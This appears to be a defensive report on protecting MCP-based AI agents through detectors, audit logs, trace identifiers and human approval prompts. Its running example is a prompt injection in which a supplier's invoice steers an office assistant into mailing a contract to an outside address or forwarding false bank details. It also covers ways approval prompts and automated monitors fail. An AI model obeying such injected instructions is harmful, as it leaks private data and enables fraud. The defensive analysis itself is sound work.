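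ProbGuard has a statistical guarantee on the error of its estimates only if it has enough recorded runs. For the household tasks, the full guarantee would need between 530 and about 100,000 runs, but the researchers used 30 per task. The method also assumes that the next state depends only on the current one, so its estimates can be wrong if the facts chosen to describe a state leave out something important.

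ProbGuard was not tested on MCP tool calls. A version for office assistants could track whether the assistant has read outside mail and opened a contract. However, probabilities learned from ordinary runs may not hold once the model is following an attacker's instruction.

### Two illustrative calculations

The figures in these examples are invented. Suppose 1 call in 10,000 is malicious, and a detector has a 99% detection rate and a 1% false alarm rate. Out of a million calls, 100 are malicious, and the detector catches 99 of them. It also raises 9,999 alarms about the 999,900 harmless calls. The share of alarms that are right is

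*99 / (99 + 9,999) ≈ 1%*.

The detector is accurate on both harmful and harmless calls, but harmless calls are so common that they cause almost all the alarms. Even with a false alarm rate of 0.4%, as in Anthropic's test, only 2.4% of alarms would come from harmful calls.

How many false alarms are tolerable depends on what happens after an alarm. If an employee has to investigate each one, 10,000 alarms would overwhelm a small team. In auto mode, the agent usually only has to make one more attempt after a false alarm, so Anthropic can tolerate many more of them.

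For the second calculation, suppose a detector misses 1% of attacks, and each miss is independent of the others. The chance that at least one of 100 attempts succeeds is

*1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 63%*.

Real attack attempts are rarely independent. If a detector always gives the same answer to the same text, an attack it blocks once will fail every time it is repeated, but an attacker who learns from each failure may need fewer than 100 attempts to succeed. Published detectors have done much worse against attackers who adapt to them than against fixed collections of attacks.

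### What NIST's proof establishes

On 9 June 2026, the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) announced a proof that no finite set of guardrails can withstand every adversarial prompt. Vassilev, a NIST scientist, had circulated the proof in a 2025 preprint, *Robust AI Security and Alignment*, and the journal *IEEE Security & Privacy* published the article in May 2026.

The proof adapts a version of Gödel's incompleteness theorem, which shows that any fixed set of mathematical rules leaves some truths unprovable. Vassilev models guardrails as a checker *C*. It returns 1 if a statement *T* is true and *p* is a proof of it that the checker can verify. The main theorem states that for every checker there is a true statement *T* about forbidden prompts such that

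*C(T, p) ≠ 1 for every p*.

The theorem assumes that the checker is a computer program, that prompts can have any length and that computing power is unlimited. It also requires infinitely many forbidden prompts, which Vassilev justifies by adding harmless text to a known one. A second theorem covers prompts of limited length. It assumes that guardrails are far fewer than possible harmful prompts, and that the AI system has every program that outputs a text of the permitted length.

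The unprovable statement in the proof is "every algorithm that outputs *x* is longer than *n*", where *x* is a forbidden prompt. That statement is about how far a program could compress the prompt, and a guardrail can block the prompt without that information. The theorem would still apply to a filter that rejected every prompt, even though that filter would let no attack through. The theorem therefore doesn't by itself show that some prompt will always get past the guardrails.

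NIST's practical advice, which doesn't depend on the proof, is to search constantly for new attacks, update guardrails against them, and prepare to limit the damage and recover quickly when one succeeds. The aim is to make attacks require more resources than attackers have.

### Detectors behind fixed rules

Supporters of detectors can accept these error rates and still argue that a detector doesn't have to work alone. The employer's mail policy already blocks sending the contract to an outside address, however the attacker words the instruction. The detector then only has to catch harmful calls the rules allow, such as the one with the false bank details, and even a modest detection rate there prevents some harm.

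This holds only if the detector can add restrictions but never remove them. If a judge's approval could override a rule, an attacker would need to fool only the judge. Auto mode applies most of the user's permission rules before it consults the judge, but it sets aside rules that would allow almost any program to run, because those rules would let dangerous commands skip the judge.

Using several detectors in a row helps less if the same text fools all of them. Anthropic reduces this risk by giving its classifier and its judge different inputs. Detectors are also harder to audit than rules, which is one reason Ravindran and Deochake prefer explicit logic for the final decision.

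### What an audit log has to record

If an attack gets past every check, investigators need a record of what the agent did. The NSA found that many MCP implementations keep no logs or record only minimal operating data, because the specification leaves audit requirements to developers. The NSA doesn't say how many implementations it examined.

Suppose the finance department has paid a false account. These entries for the assistant's `send_mail` call would help to reconstruct the incident:

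| Field | What an investigator can learn |
|---|---|
| Time and trace identifier | Which other calls belonged to the same task, and in what order |
| Verified identities of the user, agent and server | Whose authority the agent used |
| Hash of the tool's definition | Whether the tool had changed since the employee approved it |
| Exact arguments | The recipient and account number that the agent sent |
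| Policy version, rule applied and detector score | Why the checks allowed the call |
| Hash of the result | Whether a saved copy of the server's reply is genuine |

The NSA recommends logging exact arguments, identities and, where feasible, hashes of results, in a sequence that investigators can follow across sessions. It also recommends logging failed authorizations and repeated or malformed requests, which may reveal an attack in progress. Logging the definition hash and policy details helps investigators with the rug pulls and policy mistakes described earlier.

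With these entries, the investigator can trace the message to the `read_mail` call that returned the invoice. The investigator can then check the hash to confirm that the invoice in the mailbox is the one the agent read. A hash can't restore lost text, so the mail server has to keep the original.

A log also has to cover every way the agent can act. *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026), a study of agents that exceed their instructions, requires this coverage before any test, because an evaluator can't judge an unrecorded action.

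### Trace identifiers across servers

The office assistant's calls go to three servers, each with its own log. Since July 2026, the protocol no longer provides a session identifier that could connect them. Instead, the Model Context Protocol specification fixes the names of three fields from W3C Trace Context and related web standards, which travel in a request's `_meta` section: `traceparent`, `tracestate` and `baggage`. Several software libraries already used them. An entry could look like this:

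```json
"_meta": {
  "traceparent": "00-7c1e5a0f3b9d48628f40a6d2c95be713-2fa94c7be1056d38-01"
}
```

The first two digits give the format's version. The long number identifies the whole task and stays the same in every call. The next number identifies the operation that sent this request, and the last two digits show, among other things, whether the sender recorded that operation. If the mail server contacts an outside provider, it passes on the task's number with a new operation number. Software that supports OpenTelemetry, an open standard for monitoring data, can then combine all the records into one tree.

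The currency converter's developer could leave out records or attach false ones, and a trace identifier doesn't authenticate whoever sent them, so the employer should rely first on logs from its own host and gateway. The `baggage` field needs particular care because it can carry extra data to every server along the way, including outside ones. Even a complete trace shows only the order of events and doesn't prove that the invoice caused the message.

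### Tamper evidence and privacy

An attacker who takes over a machine may try to change its log. AEGIS makes such changes detectable by signing each record with a key that belongs to the agent and linking it to the previous record:

*Hₙ = SHA-256(recordₙ ‖ Hₙ₋₁)*

SHA-256 is a standard hash function, and ‖ joins the two values. If someone alters record 40, its hash changes and no longer matches the value that went into record 41. An auditor can find the break by recalculating the chain.

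However, someone with the signing key could rebuild the whole chain, and deleting the newest records leaves a shorter chain that still looks valid. To guard against both, the employer can regularly copy the latest hash to a separate system that the agent and its administrators can't change. The chain also can't reveal a call that was never logged, such as one that bypasses the libraries Yuan and colleagues patched.

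Exact arguments are often both the most useful and the most sensitive part of a log. For the office assistant, they include the text of private messages and possibly parts of the contract, so anyone who steals the log gets much of what the attacker wanted from the assistant. A full log may also contain credentials and other personal data. AEGIS searches arguments for eleven types of such data, including credit card numbers and API keys.

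The employer can remove credentials before storage, keep full arguments in a separate archive that few people can open, and delete them after a fixed period. It can also replace a value with a hash calculated using a secret key, so that nobody without the key can find a short account number by trying every possibility. An investigator could then check whether a suspected account number appeared in a call, but couldn't read an unknown one from the log. If the employer keeps full text and later has a language model search it, the instruction in the supplier's invoice reaches that model too.

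## Asking a person to approve an action

A person may notice what rules and detectors miss. For example, an employee who has paid the supplier for years might see that the account number in the message to the finance department is wrong. The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that there always be "a human in the loop with the ability to deny tool invocations". It also recommends that applications ask for confirmation of sensitive operations and show the user a tool's inputs before calling the server.

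The protocol can't make an application follow this advice, as the NSA notes by quoting the project's documentation. A server receives the same `tools/call` message whether or not anyone approved the action.

*When Neither Side Confirms* (2026) identifies two points at which software can ask the user to approve an action. The host can ask before it forwards a call, or the server can send back a question for the host to show the user, which MCP calls elicitation. If the host doesn't support elicitation, the server has to proceed or refuse without asking, and the specification doesn't settle which. Each side may therefore rely on the other to ask. A "confirmed" argument that the model fills in doesn't show that the user approved, because an injected instruction can make the model set it.

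### Three kinds of approval

| Approval | When the employee gives it | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Connecting a server | Once, during setup | Which tools the server will offer later |
| Granting access to an account | At login | Which messages the agent will send from the account |
| Allowing one call | During the task | Whether the next call is acceptable |

Problems arise when an application treats one of these approvals as if it covered another. In *Replication of Agentic Security Events* (2026), a tool that changed after approval caused harm in 15 of 16 sessions when the approval was tied to the tool's name. The changed tool caused no harm in 16 sessions when the host checked a hash of the tool's description at each call.

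Users may also have less control over individual calls than the settings suggest. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, examined five agents from Anthropic and OpenAI in May and June 2026. Anthropic's Claude chatbot once created an email draft without asking, even though it was set to "Needs approval". In Claude Cowork, a desktop agent, the researchers found no way within the application to withdraw a session's access to a folder. In chat mode, OpenAI's ChatGPT asked about every action covered by a permission, but its agent mode used a remote browser for which users could not set any permissions.

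### What a useful prompt contains

Suppose the hidden instruction in the invoice works, and the assistant tries to mail the contract to an outside address. A prompt that reads "Allow the assistant to use `send_mail`?" gives the employee no reason to refuse. A useful prompt would contain the following:

| Part | What the employee sees |
|---|---|
| Action | Send one email with an attachment; nobody can recall it afterwards |
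| Recipient | `archive@outside.example`, an address outside the company |
| Data | `contracts/supplier.pdf`, which only staff may read |
| Origin | Your request did not mention this address. It appears in the supplier's email. |

The host has to take the action, recipient and data from the call it is about to send, and the origin from its own record of the run. The data labels described earlier could supply the origin. The host shouldn't use the model's explanation, because the invoice may have influenced that too. For the message with the false bank details, the origin is the most useful part, because the employee can see from it that the account number came from an outside email.

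The exact text of a shell command may reveal little about what it does. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of agents mishandling files. Weaknesses in user review contributed to 105 of them, including 31 where the approval prompt was uninformative. A prompt for `python3 setup.py`, for example, looks routine, but approving it authorises whatever the script contains. A host could first run the command in a disposable sandbox, as Tether does, and show the user which files would change.

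The employee also needs a way to explain a refusal. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao et al., 2026) recommends distinguishing between rejecting one action and rejecting a whole approach. Otherwise, if the employee refuses to let the assistant attach the contract, the assistant might paste it into the body of the message.

### Truncated and server-written prompts

An attacker can exploit an approval prompt that shows only part of a call. *MCP-38* describes a file name with a harmless beginning and a malicious command in the part that the prompt cuts off. Users can also easily miss text that they have to scroll to see, as in the WhatsApp demonstration. The host should wrap long values onto new lines and put the recipient where the user will see it first.

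A prompt written by the server has a different weakness, because the server's developer chooses the words. The currency converter could describe an upload of the contract as "saving your exchange rate", or upload it without asking. Elicitation can therefore help a trustworthy server catch a model's mistake, but it can't protect the employee from a malicious server. Even in the host's own dialog, a display name supplied by the server can mislead, so the host should label it as the server's text and show the real tool name and arguments next to it.

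### Tool annotations

A host that asked about every call would interrupt the employee constantly. Since March 2025, servers have been able to attach annotations to their tools to help the host decide when to ask. Model Context Protocol's March 2026 blog post on the subject explains the four yes-or-no hints:

| Hint | What it claims | Value if missing | How a client can use it |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool changes nothing | False | Skip the confirmation if true |
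| `destructiveHint` | Changes may destroy something, not just add to it | True | Show a warning first if true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating the same call has no further effect | False | Retry after a failure if true |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside people or systems | True | Check the result for untrusted text if true |

The defaults are the most cautious values, so a host should treat a tool without annotations as one that may make changes, including destructive ones, and interact with outside systems. Many servers provide no annotations, and clients differ in how strictly they apply the defaults.

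Even when developers set hints honestly, the hints can be a poor guide to when the host should ask the employee for approval. `read_mail` changes nothing, but it can bring an attacker's instruction into the context. The developer of `send_mail` could reasonably mark it as non-destructive, since sending a message deletes nothing. A host that asked only about destructive tools would then send the contract without asking the employee.

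When the maintainers first discussed annotations, Justin Spahr-Summers, a co-creator of MCP, asked how a client could use a flag that it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, even a tool's display title. They compromised by treating every annotation as a hint. Clients must distrust hints unless they come from a trusted server, and each client decides how much weight to give a hint.

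A strong argument for Hosmer's position is that the defaults are already the most cautious values, so a hint can only leave a host's precautions unchanged or relax them. A host that ignores the converter's hints therefore loses convenience but no protection. For the employer's own mail server, the hints can save many prompts, as long as the host knows which servers the employer runs. According to the project's post, most clients instead treat any server the user has installed as trusted.

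**The open proposals.** The existing hints don't indicate whether a tool reads private data or whether a particular result is confidential. Such information would help a host notice when a session combines private data, untrusted text and a way to send data out. Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter*, dated 20 April 2026, lists four proposals under discussion, all of them still drafts:

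- SEP-1913, on trust and sensitivity annotations, which GitHub and OpenAI wrote after encountering gaps in their own use of MCP.
- SEP-1984, a larger set of annotations for company policies and user interfaces.
- SEP-1862, on checks before a tool runs.
- SEP-2417, on which models suit a tool.

Three smaller proposals, for hints about unsafe output, secrets and trust, had not reached the draft stage in March. The interest group that discusses these proposals can only make recommendations. It is also considering whether servers should annotate individual results. That would help with the mail server, where the same tool returns messages from colleagues and strangers.

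### How people respond to prompts

Anthropic has published the largest figures, but it also sells the automated review that it compares with human approval. It first reported that Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts, and by August 2026 it put the figure at 97%. A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness, since most requests are probably harmless. The same users also rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented, so they don't approve everything automatically.

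Anthropic's controlled study is more informative. A research vendor paid 1,053 testers to do coding work in a test environment and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Of these testers, 143 (13.6%) refused. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, which is consistent with habituation, the tendency to pay less attention to a repeated signal. Testers may have taken less care than they would with their own files, so people may refuse more often in ordinary work.

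University researchers found similar habits in a survey of 203 developers (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026, *From Delegation to Action Approval*). Of these developers, 64% often approved at least one type of action without close review. The share was 61% among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, not significantly different from the 67% among the others. Among developers who knew of at least one security incident or worrying practice, 70% often approved actions without close review, compared with 43% of the rest. Heavier use of agents might explain part of this difference, but the difference remained after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used them.

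In Salerno and colleagues' survey, 47.7% of 107 practitioners believed they read requests carefully, 33.6% skimmed them and 20.6% approved by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. Both surveys rely on self-reports from volunteers, who may overstate how careful they are.

A clear prompt does not always stop people from approving actions that go beyond the assigned task. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant for a day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the task. Every prompt described the action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount. Participants who had to approve each action still allowed 40% of the seven. They may have welcomed some of these, such as an unrequested call to the airport, which 88%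 allowed, but 35% also let the assistant read private messages.

These participants did much better than Anthropic's testers, who allowed 86% of dangerous commands. The studies differ in their participants, prompt wording, number of prompts and kind of harm, so they don't show how much of the difference came from clearer prompts.

### Ways to ask less often

Asking too often also encourages people to stop supervising altogether. In Anthropic's data, 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks. Reviewers had approved actions automatically in 80 of the 290 file incidents. There are four common ways to reduce the number of prompts:

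| Method | When the employee has to decide | Risk accepted in return |
|---|---|---|
| Approving a plan | Once, before the work starts | Text the agent reads later can fill in details the plan left open |
| Approval by risk level | Before calls rated as dangerous | A rating may be wrong, and low-risk calls can combine into a leak |
| Sandboxing | When the agent needs something outside the sandbox | The agent can damage anything inside and misuse permitted services |
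| Automated review | When the reviewing model is unsure or keeps blocking | The model misses some harmful calls, and nobody else looks at them |

The 39% rejection rate suggests that people read plans more closely than single requests. But a person approving a plan to "send the payment details to the finance department" can't check the account number, because the assistant hasn't read it yet. The host also has to check that later calls stay within the plan, as CaMeL does, or the approval won't limit what the assistant can do. A compromise is to pause for approval at a few points during the task. Salerno and colleagues cite an experiment by Zhou and colleagues in which 48 participants preferred this to a single confirmation at the end.

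Requiring approval for calls based on their severity may add little if a good policy is already in place. In a simulation in *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026), the policy had already blocked every call severe enough to require approval, so the approval step changed nothing. Requiring approval for permitted actions that depended on untrusted data worked better. It reduced the success rate of one class of attack from 23.1% to 8.7%, with 0.57 approval prompts per harmless task. The benefit shrank when the simulated reviewer became tired.

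Users can also set the risk levels themselves. One group in Yan's experiment chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data. Another group had a model decide which actions needed approval.

| Method | Prompts per person | Actions beyond the task that were blocked | Total time spent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approve every action | 18.0 | 59.6% | 142 seconds |
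| Automated review | 10.0 | 53.9% | 120 seconds |
| User's own rules | 10.9 | 39.6% | 129 seconds |

Participants chose "ask" for 81% of their rules, which postponed most decisions, and then approved two thirds of the excessive actions they were asked about. Yan assigned some later participants only to the group with rules, so the groups were not fully randomised. The automated reviewer had referred all seven excessive actions to the participants, who approved nearly half of them, so the failures in this test came from people's answers.

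With a sandbox, a person decides once which files the agent can reach instead of answering a question about each one. In Salerno and colleagues' survey, 82.2% of respondents were more willing to grant permission in a controlled environment. Anthropic considers sandboxes safe but laborious, since someone has to configure each new ability. Sandboxes also don't cover the office assistant's `send_mail` calls.

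In October 2026, Anthropic announced that automated review, already the default in Claude Code, would become the default in most of its other Claude applications on several plans. In the tester study, the reviewing model caught far more of the dangerous commands than the people did, but it missed most of the harmful actions in the stress test described in the previous section. Anthropic still recommends human review for high-stakes changes to systems in use.

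The employer could let the office assistant read mail and contracts without asking, and block it from sending attachments to outsiders. The host would then ask the employee only about rare calls that the rules can't settle, such as a message that passes payment details from an outside email to the finance department. With so few prompts, the employee is more likely to read this one. But the prompt can't show whether the account number is genuine, so the employee would still have to call the supplier on a phone number that didn't come from the invoice.
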